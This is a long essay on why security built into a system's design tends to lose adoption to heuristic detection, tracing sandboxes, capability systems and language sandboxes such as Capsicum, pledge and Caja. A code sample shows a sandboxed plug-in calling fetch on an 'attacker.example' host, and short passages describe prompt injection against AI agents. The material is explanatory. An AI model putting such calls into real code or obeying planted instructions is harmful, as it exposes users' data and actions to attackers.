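# Why security guaranteed by construction loses to heuristic detection in practice

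## What do "guaranteed by construction" and "heuristic detection" mean?

Engineers can stop attacks on a computer system in two broad ways. They can build the system so that a whole class of attack cannot succeed, or they can leave it much as it is and add a component that tries to recognise attacks as they arrive. Researchers have argued for the first way since at least the early 1970s, and in theory it usually gives stronger protection. Yet many everyday defenses, such as virus scanners, spam filters and intrusion alarms, work in the second way. Developers now face the same choice with AI systems that read mail and browse the web for their users, and the older record is some evidence of how it may turn out there.

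### One attachment, two defenses

A journalist receives a PDF from a stranger. The file contains code that exploits a bug in her PDF reader. Once the code runs, it will copy her notes and contacts to the attacker's server.

A virus scanner examines the file before the journalist opens it. The scanner compares the file's bytes with signatures, patterns that analysts have extracted from known malicious files, and may also use a statistical model to score how closely the file resembles past malware. If the score exceeds a threshold, the scanner blocks the file. A lower threshold stops more attacks but also blocks more innocent documents. The attacker can buy the same scanner and rework the file until it passes. The scanner does nothing after that. The PDF reader opens the file with all the journalist's rights, and the attacker's code runs with the same rights.

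Suppose instead that she opens the file in a viewer to which the operating system has given access to this one file, but not to her other documents or the network. The viewer does not check whether the file is malicious. The exploit, whether ten years old or new that morning, may take complete control of the viewer, but it still cannot read her contacts or send them anywhere.

Dangerzone, a free program from the Freedom of the Press Foundation, comes close to this description. It opens a suspicious document inside an isolated compartment without network access, turns each page into a grid of pixels, and builds a new PDF from the pixels. According to *Safe Ride into the Dangerzone* (Métaireau, Pyrgiotis and Perot, 2024), the design assumes that determined attackers will find a hole in the office software that opens the document and take over that software. The Mac version takes up 2.2 GB because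 it includes its own Linux virtual machine and a copy of the LibreOffice suite, according to The Eclectic Light Company's *How to open a suspicious document or app* (2026). The journalist also gets back a picture of the document with a searchable text layer, so a spreadsheet loses its formulas.

### What each defense promises

The viewer provides a guarantee by construction, which means that the way it is built makes a property hold for every input within a stated threat model. A threat model describes what the attacker can do and what the defender is trying to protect. The scanner performs heuristic detection, which means that it recognises probable attacks using signatures, statistics or a trained model, but misses some attacks and raises some false alarms.

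Saltzer and Schroeder drew much the same distinction in *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (1975), where one of their eight design principles is to base access decisions on permission rather than exclusion. The viewer can access only what somebody has granted it, whereas the scanner lets through everything it has no reason to block. They argued that a mistake in a permission-based mechanism tends to refuse legitimate access, which people notice quickly, while a mistake in an exclusion-based mechanism tends to allow access that should be refused, which may go unnoticed in normal use.

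For security, that is an argument for permission, but it is also commercially awkward, a point Saltzer and Schroeder did not dwell on. When a permission-based design fails, paying users see features that do not work, while a detector's misses go unnoticed until an attack succeeds.

The two kinds of defense also need different evidence. A detector's maker can test it against a collection of attacks and report a detection rate for that collection. A guarantee needs an argument about all inputs, which no amount of testing supplies. Anderson (1972), in *Computer Security Technology Planning Study*, made this point to the US Air Force about "tiger teams", groups of experts who try to break into a system. A successful break-in reveals a flaw, but a failed attempt leaves the system's security unknown. Anderson added that no known team had yet failed.

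### The parts of a guarantee

Anderson's study also supplied the standard account of what has to be in place before a guarantee deserves the name. The Air Force wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer, and it had to assume that one of them might write hostile programs. The study proposed a reference monitor, a component that checks every attempt by a program to use data, a device or another program against a list of what the program's user may do. The mechanism has to satisfy three requirements:

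- it must be tamper-proof, since an attacker who can alter it can switch it off;
- every access must go through it, with no exempt programs;
- it must be small enough for people to analyse and test completely.

The three requirements depend on one another, as Anderson showed with a Honeywell mainframe running the GCOS III operating system. The hardware confined each program to its own region of memory, which resembles a reference monitor. But whenever a program needed to read or write a file, the operating system did the work on its behalf, and most of the operating system ran with the memory check suspended, so the check did not cover every access. Counting the operating system as part of the monitor would make the monitor too large to analyse in full, since the operating system had between 200,000 and 300,000 instructions. Several break-ins had also already shown that it was not tamper-proof.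 Anderson concluded that a system not designed for security from the start was unlikely to become secure by retrofit, that is, by adding a defense to existing software without rewriting it.

The trusted computing base is everything that must work correctly for a guarantee to hold. NIST, the US standards agency, defines it in its glossary entry *trusted computing base (TCB)* as all the hardware, firmware and software protection mechanisms that together enforce a security policy. "Trusted" means only that the guarantee depends on these parts, so a flaw in any of them can void it.

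Designers can reduce the amount of software that a guarantee depends on, as Dangerzone's developers did in 2024. Before version 0.7.0, its isolated converter made requests directly to the Linux kernel, the privileged core of the operating system, and a kernel bug within reach of those requests could have let an attacker out. The developers put gVisor in between, a Google program that acts as the converter's kernel and handles most requests itself. It is much smaller than Linux and is written in Go, a language that rules out many of the bugs found in Linux. Métaireau and colleagues report that an attacker must now break out of gVisor before reaching Linux. The guarantee still depends on software that could have holes, and programs that make very many system requests run more slowly under gVisor.

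Two more terms describe how the viewer differs from an ordinary PDF reader. Least privilege is Saltzer and Schroeder's principle that every program and every user should operate with the smallest set of rights the job requires. The usual obstacle to it is ambient authority, the rights a program has merely because of who runs it. Miller, Yee and Shapiro's *Capability Myths Demolished* defines this as authority that is "exercised, but not selected, by its user" and gives the example of the Unix function that opens a file. A program calls the function with a file name and no credential, and the system allows or refuses the request based on the account the program runs under. This is why the journalist's PDF reader can open her contacts as well as the attachment, and why an exploit inside the reader can too. The alternative is to give a program a capability, an unforgeable reference that both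 names an object and carries the right to use it.

A program is memory-safe if it accesses only memory it validly holds, within bounds and while that memory is still allocated. In languages such as C, the programmer has to ensure this. If a PDF declares an image to be smaller than it is, a program that trusts the declared size may copy the surplus bytes over neighboring data and end up running them as instructions. Watson, Baldwin and colleagues (2025) report in *It is time to standardize principles and practices for software memory safety* that such bugs have made up around two thirds of critical vulnerabilities for more than twenty years in every major systems software base, including Windows, Linux, Android and iOS. A memory-safe language prevents these bugs by construction, except in any unsafe code that remains in its own trusted computing base. A scanner can only look for files that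 seem to exploit them.

The same terms apply to AI agents, which are language models that act through tools such as mail, files or a browser. In a prompt injection, someone plants instructions in text that an AI system reads, and the system follows them. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, 2026) treats this as an authorization problem, because the damage comes from an action the agent had the means to carry out, such as leaking a record or transferring money. Structural defenses therefore limit what an agent can do, whatever instructions its model has taken in.

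### Defenses that work by chance

Some widely used protections are neither guaranteed by construction nor heuristic detection. Address space layout randomisation, for example, places a program's code and data at unpredictable positions in memory each time the program starts. To exploit a memory bug, an attacker often needs to know where something is in memory, and now has to guess. This isn't detection, because nothing is checked for signs of an attack, and it isn't guaranteed by construction, because an input that contains a correct guess can still succeed.

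If the layout has *N* equally likely positions, one blind guess succeeds with probability 1/*N*, and at least one of *m* independent guesses succeeds with probability 1 − (1 − 1/*N*)^*m*. With 65,536 positions, a single guess almost always fails, but 65,536 guesses have about a 63% chance of at least one success. A wrong guess usually crashes the program, so the defense depends heavily on whether the program restarts by itself and whether anyone is watching the crashes. An attacker who finds a second bug that leaks an address may not need to guess at all. Watson and colleagues write that such mitigations frequently fail in the longer term partly because they rely on secrets that can be leaked or guessed. They reserve the phrase "strong memory safety" for techniques that don't depend on chance.

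Saltzer and Schroeder describe a mechanism's work factor as the effort needed to defeat it, compared with the attacker's resources. There are 456,976 possible four-letter passwords, which is enough against someone typing guesses at a terminal but not against a computer that tries a million per second. A probabilistic mitigation has a work factor of this kind. They observed that many protection mechanisms do not, because systematic attack is logically impossible and the intruder has to wait for a hardware failure or search for an error in the implementation. Nobody can reliably say how long that search will take, so the strength of a guarantee is hard to estimate.

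### Sound, and still beaten

A guarantee covers only the threats in its threat model. Anderson's first step in building a secure system was to define which threats it should withstand, and the study then listed what the reference monitor left out. The study assumed that the system had correctly identified every user, that guards and locks protected the machines, that nobody was tampering with the communication lines, and that the hardware worked. An attacker can bypass the monitor by attacking any of these. Similarly, parameterised queries stop a database from reading user input as a command, but they don't protect against a stolen administrator password.

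In the journalist's case, the attacker might send a PDF that contains no exploit, only a convincing invoice with a new bank account number. Dangerzone would convert it to pixels and back, and the account number would come through intact. The isolation would work as designed, but the journalist could still send the attacker money. A mail filter trained on fraudulent invoices might catch it. An advantage of detection is that it can target attacks that nobody knows how to rule out by design, including those that deceive the reader instead of exploiting the software.

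A system can also be guaranteed to enforce the wrong rules, and security engineers call a system's rules its policy. If an administrator sets a policy that lets the viewer use the network to load remote images, the journalist's document can be sent out over the same network, even if the isolation has no flaw. Narisetty and colleagues describe a similar weakness in defenses for AI agents, which typically label whatever the user types as trustworthy. If someone tricks the user into pasting in hostile text, that text is labeled trustworthy too, and every later check relies on the wrong label.

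Saltzer and Schroeder pointed out in 1975 that preventing all unauthorized use is a negative requirement. To show that a system meets it, one must show that its designers anticipated every possible threat. They warned that concentrating on mechanisms that are "logically impossible to defeat" may create false confidence in the system as a whole. A guarantee still has an advantage within its threat model, because an attacker gains nothing by trying again, whereas repeated attempts can help against a detector. But claims about which approach is stronger mean little unless we specify which attacks we are considering.

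### Which defense carries the weight

Few real systems use only one approach. According to Métaireau and colleagues, Google uses gVisor when it scans Gmail attachments for viruses, so the detector runs inside a sandbox. Microsoft's Application Guard for Office opened untrusted documents in a container separated from the rest of the computer by hardware virtualization. When a user wanted to take a file out, an optional service first checked it for malware.

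One can tell which approach a system depends on by asking what happens when the detector misses an attack. While the document stays inside Application Guard, a miss does little harm, because the container still separates the attacker from the company's data. Once the user has removed that protection, a miss may do a great deal of harm. The same product can therefore depend on construction at one moment and on detection the next, and the history of these defenses largely depends on how often users and administrators have reason to switch from one to the other.

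### What counts as losing

To say that guarantees "lose" is to make a claim about adoption, which can fail at several points. Five stages are useful for placing a defense:

1. Prototype: researchers have built it and shown that it works.
2. Available product: an outsider can obtain it and use it for real work.
3. Opt-in feature: it comes with something people already use, but somebody has to turn it on.
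4. Default: it is on unless somebody turns it off.
5. Majority use: most of the systems that could have it do have it and run it.

A guarantee loses to detection when it stalls at an early stage of adoption, or slips back to one, while detectors aimed at the same attacks become the default. This can happen even if its security argument remains sound. Dangerzone is at the second stage. Anyone can install it, but they have to know about it and download it themselves.

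Application Guard for Office reached the third stage, but Microsoft retired it in April 2024. Only organisations with certain premium licences could use it, and their administrators had to enable it. Inside the container, macros and add-ins did not run, and Office could not access the user's identity or arbitrary files, so ordinary actions such as sharing a document or inserting a picture from the disk could fail. In a notice to administrators, Microsoft (2025) scheduled the feature's removal from Office in two phases, starting in February 2026 and finishing between early December 2026 and July 2027, depending on the update channel. It cited the end of support for a version of Windows and a more streamlined security experience.

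Documents that used to open in the container now open in Protected View, an older mode that keeps them read-only until the user chooses to edit. Microsoft also advises administrators to turn on rules that block risky behavior in Office files and a control that lets only trusted, signed code run. Protected View and the signed-code control are restrictions rather than detectors, so the container was largely replaced by looser restrictions that take fewer resources. Application Guard allowed light editing inside the container, whereas a user who wants to edit a file in Protected View has to leave that mode, which means deciding that the file is probably safe.

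## Why did capability-based operating systems stay rare?

An operating system built entirely on capabilities has no ambient authority, so a program starts with only the references it is given. Jack Dennis and Earl Van Horn described the idea in 1966, and researchers had working systems in the 1970s. But nearly every desktop computer and server still runs a system in which programs inherit their user's rights.

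### How a capability works

KeyKOS, a 1980s mainframe operating system, kept capabilities and data in separate kinds of storage (Rajunas, Hardy and colleagues, *Security in KeyKOS*, 1986). A page held 4,096 bytes of code or data, and a node held sixteen slots for capabilities, which KeyKOS called keys. Programs could change the bytes in their pages, but only the kernel handled the contents of the slots.

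To use an object, a program asked the kernel to invoke the key in a numbered slot. The kernel looked up which object the key referred to and what it permitted, and carried out the request if the key allowed it. A program could use only the keys in its slots, and could not forge a key by computing the right string of bytes. It received new keys from its creator or in messages, which could carry up to four keys each. Sending a message also required a key to the recipient.

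An access control list instead stores permissions with the object. Each file has a list of users and what they may do with it. When a program asks for a file by name, the system checks whether the program's user account is on the list. The file's name and the permission to use the file can therefore come from different parties.

### The confused deputy

Norm Hardy, later senior architect at Key Logic, the company behind KeyKOS, saw the consequences at Tymshare, a firm that sold time on shared computers. His *The Confused Deputy* (1988) describes an incident there from about eleven years earlier. Tymshare kept a compiler in a directory called SYSX, and users who ran it could name a file to receive debugging output. The compiler had permission to write to SYSX because it kept a file of its own there. The directory also held the billing records, in a file called BILL. When a user named BILL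 as the debugging file, the compiler overwrote the records.

The access control worked as designed. The user had no right to write to BILL, but the compiler did, and the request came from the compiler. The system had no way to detect that the user had chosen the name. The compiler's author could have added a check on whether the user was allowed to write to the named file. But programmers have to remember such a check wherever their program opens a file on someone else's behalf, and another program may change what the name refers to between the check and the write.

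With capabilities, the administrator gives the compiler a capability to its own file in SYSX but none to BILL. A user who wants debugging output passes the compiler a capability to the output file. The user has no capability to BILL and cannot pass one, so the compiler does not need to check the file it is given.

*The Confused Deputy*, a set of lecture slides from UT Austin, shows the same repair on ordinary Unix. Unix programs refer to an open file by a small number, its file descriptor, and one program can pass a descriptor to another. A launcher opens the debugging file with limited rights and passes the descriptor to the compiler. Miller and colleagues consider file descriptors nearly equivalent to capabilities. Unix has thus had most of the mechanism for decades, but it also lets programs open files by name, and most programs do so.

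Confusion is still possible with capabilities. Miller and colleagues point out that a program holding several capabilities can go wrong if it tries each one until one works. To avoid this, it has to remember which capability it received for which purpose.

### From Hydra to EROS

Carnegie Mellon University developed Hydra in the 1970s for C.mmp, an experimental multiprocessor. Cambridge University's CAP computer, running by the mid-1970s, went further and checked capabilities in purpose-built hardware. Both were influential research projects that never became products. (Intel's attempt at a commercial capability processor, the iAPX 432, belongs to the history of hardware.)

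KeyKOS became a product that ran on IBM and Amdahl mainframes and had supported commercial applications since 1983. A security policy depended on 25,000 lines of assembler in the kernel and another 25,000 lines outside it. Together they were at most a quarter the size of GCOS III, which Anderson had judged too large to analyse. Passing control and a message from one protected program to another took about 200 machine instructions, which Rajunas and colleagues considered reasonable for a complete change of code, memory and access rights.

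KeyKOS could also run CMS, IBM's interactive environment, and most software development on KeyKOS took place inside it. This let users keep their existing software, but it also removed much of the reason to switch. Programs written for CMS still looked up their files by name, and KeyKOS could isolate the whole environment without dividing up the rights inside it. Finer protection required new software written to use keys. KeyKOS did not last as a commercial product.

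Jonathan Shapiro started EROS at the University of Pennsylvania in the 1990s to bring the KeyKOS design to ordinary PC hardware. Work on it ended in the mid-2000s. Shapiro designed a successor, Coyotos, and Charles Landau, who co-wrote the KeyKOS paper, continued the EROS code as CapROS. Neither system became widely used.

### Three myths and a harder objection

Miller and colleagues, writing in 2003, blamed part of this neglect on three beliefs that research papers had repeated for about twenty years.

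Miller and colleagues call it a myth that access control lists and capabilities are equivalent, even though both can store the same table of permissions. If the table has users down the side and files along the top, an access control list is a column and a program's set of capabilities is a row. They argue that the table shows the permissions at one moment and omits the rules for changing them. In practice, access control lists name user accounts, because administrators have to keep track of who is on them. Capability systems treat every running program as a separate holder of rights, so a user can start a program with a small part of her own authority without asking an administrator to create an account for it.

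The confinement myth is the mistaken belief that capability systems cannot stop rights from spreading, since anyone who holds a capability can pass it on. The usual source is a 1984 argument by Earl Boebert. Suppose Alice has low clearance and Bob has high clearance. Alice can write to a low-level file, and she stores her write capability in that file. Bob, who may read low-level files, takes the capability and uses it to copy secrets into the file, where Alice can read them. This attack works only if anyone who can read a file's data can also read the capabilities stored in it. KeyKOS and EROS made these separate rights, so Bob could be allowed to read the file's data without obtaining Alice's capability.

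The irrevocability myth is literally correct that nobody can take a capability back, but Alice can still revoke the access she gives Bob. She gives him a capability to a forwarder, a small object that passes his requests on to the file. When she wants to end his access, she tells the forwarder to stop. Bob's capability then no longer works, nor do any copies he shared. David Redell described this method in 1974.

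These answers are convincing, but Miller and colleagues quote researchers, not the people who built or bought operating systems, so their evidence doesn't show how many products the myths prevented. Confusion certainly lasted. In 2017 the blog Habitat Chronicles complained that nearly all explanations of capabilities were very long, very old or buried in the documentation of a particular language or system. Capabilities also had informed sceptics. In 2015 a critic on a cryptography mailing list accused Miller and colleagues of choosing examples that suit capabilities, and argued that access control lists work better when the hard question is who belongs to a group.

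Smalley (1999) raised a more serious objection in *Capability-Based Systems*, arguing that an organisation's security policy has to control how access rights spread, whereas a capability lets its holder decide. Hydra and KeyKOS had added mechanisms to limit this, but Smalley thought these generally supported only the policies they were designed for, and that the added complexity made capabilities much less appealing. Smalley's own project, Flask, kept capabilities to limit programs' rights but had a separate component decide what the policy allowed.

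The KeyKOS developers had already argued that controlling the connections between objects made security labels on individual objects unnecessary. They wanted the kernel to provide mechanisms and leave policy to programs above it. A trusted program called a factory could inspect a new object before anyone used it and certify that it held no keys through which data could escape.

Capability systems handle a policy fixed in advance better than one that changes. Suppose a contractor's clearance lapses and an administrator needs to know today which files the contractor can reach. With access control lists, the administrator can search the lists for the contractor's name. In KeyKOS, finding the answer required a database of connections, which existed only as a prototype in 1986, and cutting off access required someone to have already put forwarders in the right places. This was a real problem for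 the US Department of Defense, an important customer for secure systems, because it required records of who could access what.

### Capsicum and pledge

Central policy matters much less when the aim is to protect one user from a hijacked program. Two Unix-like systems have tried to do this in different ways, and their results are the closest thing available to a natural experiment.

Capsicum, published in 2010, adds real capabilities to FreeBSD. According to the University of Cambridge's *Capsicum* page, it first appeared in FreeBSD 9.0 as an experimental option and became part of the standard kernel in 10.0. Capsicum attaches a list of rights to each file descriptor, and a program can remove rights from the list but not add them. A program that calls `cap_enter` permanently loses the ability to open anything by a system-wide name. It can then use only descriptors that it already holds, receives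 from other programs, or derives from these, such as one for a file inside a directory it has already opened.

How much work it takes to adapt a program to Capsicum depends on the program. Capsicum's designers needed around ten lines for the network tool tcpdump and about 100 for the Chromium browser, which already ran as several processes. *Sandbox Your Program Using FreeBSD's Capsicum* (Freeland, 2025) recommends opening all the files a program will need and then calling `cap_enter`. A developer who can't predict what the program will need can either split it in two and sandbox only the dangerous half, or have it send requests to Casper, a set of helper processes outside the sandbox. Even looking up an internet address goes through Casper, and the developer has to replace the ordinary lookup function with a special version.

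OpenBSD's pledge, which arrived in 2015 and shipped in full in 2016, is much simpler. The program declares which kinds of operation it will need from then on. For example, `pledge("stdio rpath", NULL)` allows basic input and output plus reading files, and looking up internet addresses requires only the word `dns`. OpenBSD's *pledge(2)* manual page describes about three dozen such categories, and in most cases the kernel kills a program that attempts an operation outside the ones it declared.

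Theo de Raadt, who leads OpenBSD, wrote in 2015 slides that only 12 programs had used Capsicum, that it required "intense modification of existing programs", and that it failed three of his tests: ease of use, applicability, and whether its use could be mandatory.

Kees Cook, a Linux security developer, questioned the last of these in *evolution of seccomp* (2015). Programs have to opt in to pledge too, and OpenBSD's kernel still runs programs that don't. Cook supposed that de Raadt meant a protection stops being optional in practice once developers have built it into everything. OpenBSD's developers worked that way, and by the 2016 release they had converted 453 of the 707 programs in the base system, which the project maintains itself.

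An OpenBSD developer argued in flak's *going full pledge* (2015) that an interface may suit the first five programs and then prove so awkward that nobody bothers with the next five, while a hundred conversions are good evidence that the next hundred will go well. OpenBSD later had a "magic 50 programs rule" for judging whether unveil, a companion to pledge that limits which files a program can see, was ready for release. Converting programs to use pledge also exposed bad designs. OpenBSD's `patch` tool, which applies changes to text files, handled one format by running the editor `ed`, which can execute arbitrary commands. Adding pledge led the developers to rewrite `patch` so that it no longer ran another program.

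In *Sandboxing Adoption in Open Source Ecosystems* (2024), Alhindi and Hallett measured sandboxing adoption in 2023 by searching the source code of each system's packages, mostly programs by outside developers, and counting the sandboxed processes running after a fresh installation. They also compared the sandboxing code in gmid, a small server that runs on both systems.

| | Capsicum on FreeBSD | pledge and unveil on OpenBSD |
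|---|---|---|
| Early conversions | 12 programs (de Raadt's count, 2015) | 453 of 707 base programs (2016) |
| Sandboxed processes after startup | 3 of 47 | 33 of 36 |
| Packages that use it directly | 43 of 30,763 (0.14%) | 114 of 7,700 (1.48%) |
| Lines of sandboxing code in gmid | 28 | 96 |

Lines of code evidently don't explain the difference, since gmid needed fewer for Capsicum than for pledge. But Capsicum's restrictions pass to every program a sandboxed program starts, and gmid has to start scripts that need wider rights. Its developer therefore had to split the server into two processes, only one of which could be sandboxed under Capsicum, while both could be under pledge. The main difficulty in adopting Capsicum is often a redesign of this kind, which a line count doesn't measure.

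Capsicum's defenders reply that pledge is easy because it guarantees less. Jonathan Anderson, one of Capsicum's designers (not the Anderson of the 1972 study), argues in *A comparison of Unix sandboxing techniques* (2017) that a word processor that has to save one document must pledge `wpath`, which lets it write to any file the user can. And if a program keeps the right to start other programs, an attacker who takes it over can start an unrestricted one. Jonathan Anderson concludes that pledge is a mitigation for catching unskilled attackers and not a basis for rigorous policy. He also shows that bhyve, FreeBSD's virtual machine program, needed fewer than ten added lines to enter Capsicum's sandbox. Freeland calls pledge's categories "privilege silos" because a program that needs one right in a category has to take the rest, though he concedes that Casper's services have a similar flaw unless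 the developer restricts them.

OpenBSD has since dealt with part of this criticism. Unveil, released in 2018, can limit the word processor to one folder, and a program can now also declare limits for the programs it starts. But developers have to add these too, and Alhindi and Hallett found pledge in 111 packages but unveil in only 36.

Pledge's easier interface probably accounts for some of the tenfold gap between OpenBSD's and FreeBSD's packages, but pledge became nearly universal only where one group maintained all the code and had decided to convert it. The leader of OpenBSD, a security-focused project, wanted every base program converted, and FreeBSD had no comparable campaign. OpenBSD's own packages suggest how much that campaign mattered. Pledge covers almost every OpenBSD process at startup but appears in fewer than one in sixty packages, though the packages include fonts, documentation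 and programs in languages that the search did not cover.

*A Measurement Study on the Adoption of Pledges and Unveils* (Ruohonen, Sierszecki and Tiwari, 2026) followed 19 OpenBSD releases and found that adoption of the sandboxing calls pledge and unveil grew roughly in a straight line. Larger programs did not consistently need more of the calls. The paper concludes that sandboxing is not necessarily as troublesome to adopt as the literature often suggests.

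### Where capabilities run today

Full capability systems have done best where there is little old software to carry over, or where one company controls most of it. The microkernel seL4 controls all access through capabilities, and in 2009 its developers completed a machine-checked proof that its C code matches its specification. That meets Anderson's demand for a reference monitor small enough to analyse completely. The Chinese carmaker NIO has put seL4 into production cars. But developers often run Linux in a virtual machine on seL4, and programs in that virtual machine have the same ambient authority as on any other Linux system.

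Google's Fuchsia gives each process a set of handles, each of which refers to a kernel object and specifies what the process can do with it. In 2021 Google began replacing the Linux-based software on its Nest Hub smart displays with Fuchsia, and the interface looked much the same afterwards. Google could do this because it wrote most of the software on the device and did not need thousands of outside developers to convert their programs.

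WebAssembly, a portable format for compiled programs, lets many developers recompile old code for a capability system without restructuring it, which removes much of the work that limited Capsicum's adoption. Its system interface, WASI, descends from Capsicum through an earlier project called CloudABI. Under WASI, a program starts with no access to files, and whoever runs it grants access to particular directories. A program written for Unix can still ask for a file by its path, because WASI's C library translates the request into a lookup inside a directory the program has received.

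## What happened to programming languages built on capabilities?

WASI limits what a whole program can access, but most programs contain code by many authors, and all of that code usually has the same rights. A charting library in a banking app may be able to read the customer's password as easily as the bank's own code can. Since the 1990s, a few language designers have tried to use capabilities to limit what each part of a program can access.

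### The object-capability model

Programs in many modern languages consist largely of objects, which combine data with functions that act on it. One object can use another only through a reference to it, and in a memory-safe language no code can forge a reference, so a reference is already close to a capability. Mark Miller, who co-wrote *Capability Myths Demolished*, adds two conditions in the slides *Secure Distributed Programming on EcmaScript 5 + HTML5 platforms*: code may affect the world outside itself only through references it holds, and it starts with no powerful ones.

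Under these rules, code can use an object only if it created the object, received it from its own creator, had it from the start, or got it from other code that already held it. In one of Miller's examples, Alice makes a counter with two functions, one that adds one and one that subtracts one. She gives the adding function to Bob's code and the subtracting function to Carol's, so Bob can only count up and Carol can only count down. Alice doesn't need to write a list of permissions.

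Most languages break the rules by giving all code ambient authority over files and the network, and by having global mutable state, which is data that every part of the program can change. Ihab Awad, who worked with Miller at Google, says in *Google Caja* that removing such shared objects is hard because most languages are full of them.

The following program runs a plug-in that can write to a log and do little else. It uses Hardened JavaScript, a restricted mode of the web's main programming language.

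```
lockdown();
const lines = [];
const log = harden({ write(text) { lines.push(text); } });
const box = new Compartment({ globals: harden({ log }), __options__: true });
box.evaluate(`log.write("plug-in started")`);
box.evaluate(`fetch("https://attacker.example")`);  // fails
```

The third line makes a logger whose `write` function adds text to a list. The fourth creates a compartment, a sandbox with its own global names, and puts the logger into it. The text in the last two lines is the plug-in's code. It can write to the log, but its attempt to contact a website fails because the compartment has no `fetch` function. The plug-in cannot read the log either, since it received the logger and not the list.

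The call to `lockdown` closes some less obvious routes. In ordinary JavaScript, every function is linked to a built-in constructor that turns text into running code, and that code can use the program's real global objects. A plug-in could follow the link from `log.write` and get `fetch` back. It could also replace the `push` function that all lists share and see whatever the rest of the program adds with it. After `lockdown`, the constructor throws an error and the shared built-ins can no longer change.

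### E, Joe-E and Caja

Miller and others created E in the late 1990s as a new language that followed these rules throughout. It ran on top of Java, but E programs could use Java's libraries only through wrappers that withheld the dangerous functions. Researchers at the University of California, Berkeley, published Joe-E, a subset of Java, in 2010. A checking program rejected code that relied on global mutable state or opened files without being given the right to. Code that passed was ordinary Java, so programmers could keep their compiler and editor, but they could not use any library that broke the rules. Neither language gained many users outside research.

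Caja reached far more people. Around 2008, large websites wanted to show small applications by outside developers, but a script placed directly in a web page can read and change everything on it. Miller, Samuel and colleagues (2008) noted in *Caja* that web applications generally dealt with this by removing scripts from outside content. Their Google project instead rewrote the scripts and then let them in.

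*JavaScript Sandboxing* (Van Acker and Sabelfeld, 2016) describes the method. A translator on the website's server removed features such as `eval`, which runs text as code. It wrapped each outside script in a function that cut the script off from the page's global names, and it inserted checks that ran in the browser. The page then gave the script versions of the page's objects that exposed only selected features.

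In December 2008 Yahoo opened My Yahoo and Yahoo Mail to outside applications and used Caja to contain them. The developer Simon Willison (2008) wrote that Caja suddenly had 275 million users, and guessed that this made it the most widely used capability language ever. Yahoo had chosen Caja for those users, most of whom had probably never heard of it, and developers who wanted to reach them had to follow Caja's rules.

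Those rules made developers give up a good deal of compatibility. In *Some Thoughts Regarding Caja*, West (2008) accepted that Yahoo needed something like Caja because it could not review thousands of applications by hand. But Caja turned a page's HTML into JavaScript instructions for building the page, so even a plain search form stopped working for anyone without JavaScript.

Existing libraries were a bigger obstacle. A Caja developer posted *Innocent code vs Caja* to a forum for the popular library jQuery and attached a copy of jQuery in which the team had changed every loop of one common kind to get around a single incompatibility. Ficarra's *Google Caja: Popular Library Cajoling* proposed a 2010 student project just to find out what stopped jQuery and two similar libraries from passing through the translator. O'Reilly's *Use Precajoled JavaScript Libraries* credits library developers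 with getting at least some of their functions through it. Facebook and others had their own restricted versions of JavaScript, and Van Acker and Sabelfeld thought it unrealistic to expect library authors to write a separate edition for each.

Caja's effect on speed is less clear, because Van Acker and Sabelfeld found no published measurements. By 2020 Caja no longer needed the translator. The 2009 edition of the JavaScript standard had added features such as `Object.freeze`, which fixes an object's properties and which Awad credits to Miller's advocacy. With these features, a small start-up script in the browser could set up a safe subset called Secure ECMAScript, or SES. A developer asked about speed in a mailing-list thread, Power's *Caja performance recommendations* (2020). Kevin Reid of the Caja team answered that SES significantly slowed JavaScript down and that Caja's handling of HTML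 and CSS added more work. Miller replied a few hours later that the overhead of SES was negligible.

Google had by then replaced Caja in its own Apps Script, a tool for extending Google's office software. Caja had contained the scripts that people wrote for the tool. In December 2014 Google offered an alternative based on the iframe, a page within a page that the browser can keep separate from the page around it. Gupta (2015), in *Google Apps Script*, told developers that the iframe gave them faster interfaces and a choice of JavaScript libraries. According to Google's *Enum SandboxMode*, the iframe also imposed "many fewer restrictions", and all scripts used it from July 2016.

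Google archived Caja in January 2021, explaining that nobody had kept it up to date with web security research and that Google engineers and outside researchers had reported several vulnerabilities. Caja had to wrap every browser feature that an outside script might use, so its guarantee depended on constant maintenance.

The sandboxed iframe that replaced Caja also guarantees security by construction, so Caja did not lose to detection. The iframe is coarser because its code and the surrounding page can exchange only messages, while Caja also let them share live objects. Reid recommended iframes in 2020 for outside widgets that do not need complex interaction with the page, and browser makers were maintaining them anyway.

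### Java's Security Manager

Java's first release in the 1990s included the Security Manager, which restricted untrusted code. It was a permission system rather than a capability system, because any code could request any file by name. For each request, the Security Manager checked that all the code in the chain of calls leading to it had permission. This prevented untrusted code from gaining a trusted library's rights simply by calling it, which is one answer to the confused deputy problem.

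The check also complicated harmless requests. In *JEP 486*, Mullan and Buckley give the example of a program that has no right to read files and asks for the local time. Java's library has to read a time-zone file to answer, so it had to declare that it was acting on its own authority. Over 1,200 methods in Java's libraries had to raise their privileges this way, and over 1,000 had to check permissions.

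Java's designers built the Security Manager for applets, small programs that a browser downloaded and ran, and later extended it to all Java code. Applets died out, and the wider use never caught on. OpenJDK's *JEP 411* (2021), the proposal to phase the Security Manager out, lists several reasons:

- Developers had to grant every permission an application needed. Someone who only wanted to limit which files it could read also had to work out its permissions for everything else.
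- When a library needed a permission, the application calling it usually needed the same one. Developers often gave up and granted everything.
- The checks were slow enough that Java left the Security Manager off by default, so library authors had little reason to support it.
- It could not address 19 of the 25 most dangerous kinds of software weakness on an industry list from 2020. Many of these involve malicious data and not malicious code.

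Java 17 began printing a warning whenever someone enabled the Security Manager, and Mullan and Buckley report that hardly anyone discussed the warnings. They add that most of the few applications that used it granted all permissions to their code. Oracle's *The Security Manager Is Permanently Disabled* confirms that nobody can enable it in Java 24, released in 2025.

The maintainers wanted to remove a feature that took a lot of work to maintain, so their account is not neutral, but the silence after Java 17 is hard to explain if many people relied on it. Opponents campaigned on a site called *Discuss JEP 411*, arguing that an application rarely needs everything Java can do and that the unused abilities only help attackers. Mullan and Buckley recommend containers and operating-system sandboxes, which they consider easier to learn and use. These restrict a whole Java program at once, so a library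 taken over by an attacker still has every right that the rest of the program needs.

### Hardened JavaScript and LavaMoat

Hardened JavaScript, which developed from Caja's SES, is mainly used to fill that gap. The project's site, *Hardened JavaScript*, lists three companies that use it. Agoric uses it to confine smart contracts, and Moddable uses it to confine programs on small devices. MetaMask, a cryptocurrency wallet, uses it for plug-ins and for the third-party packages in its browser extension.

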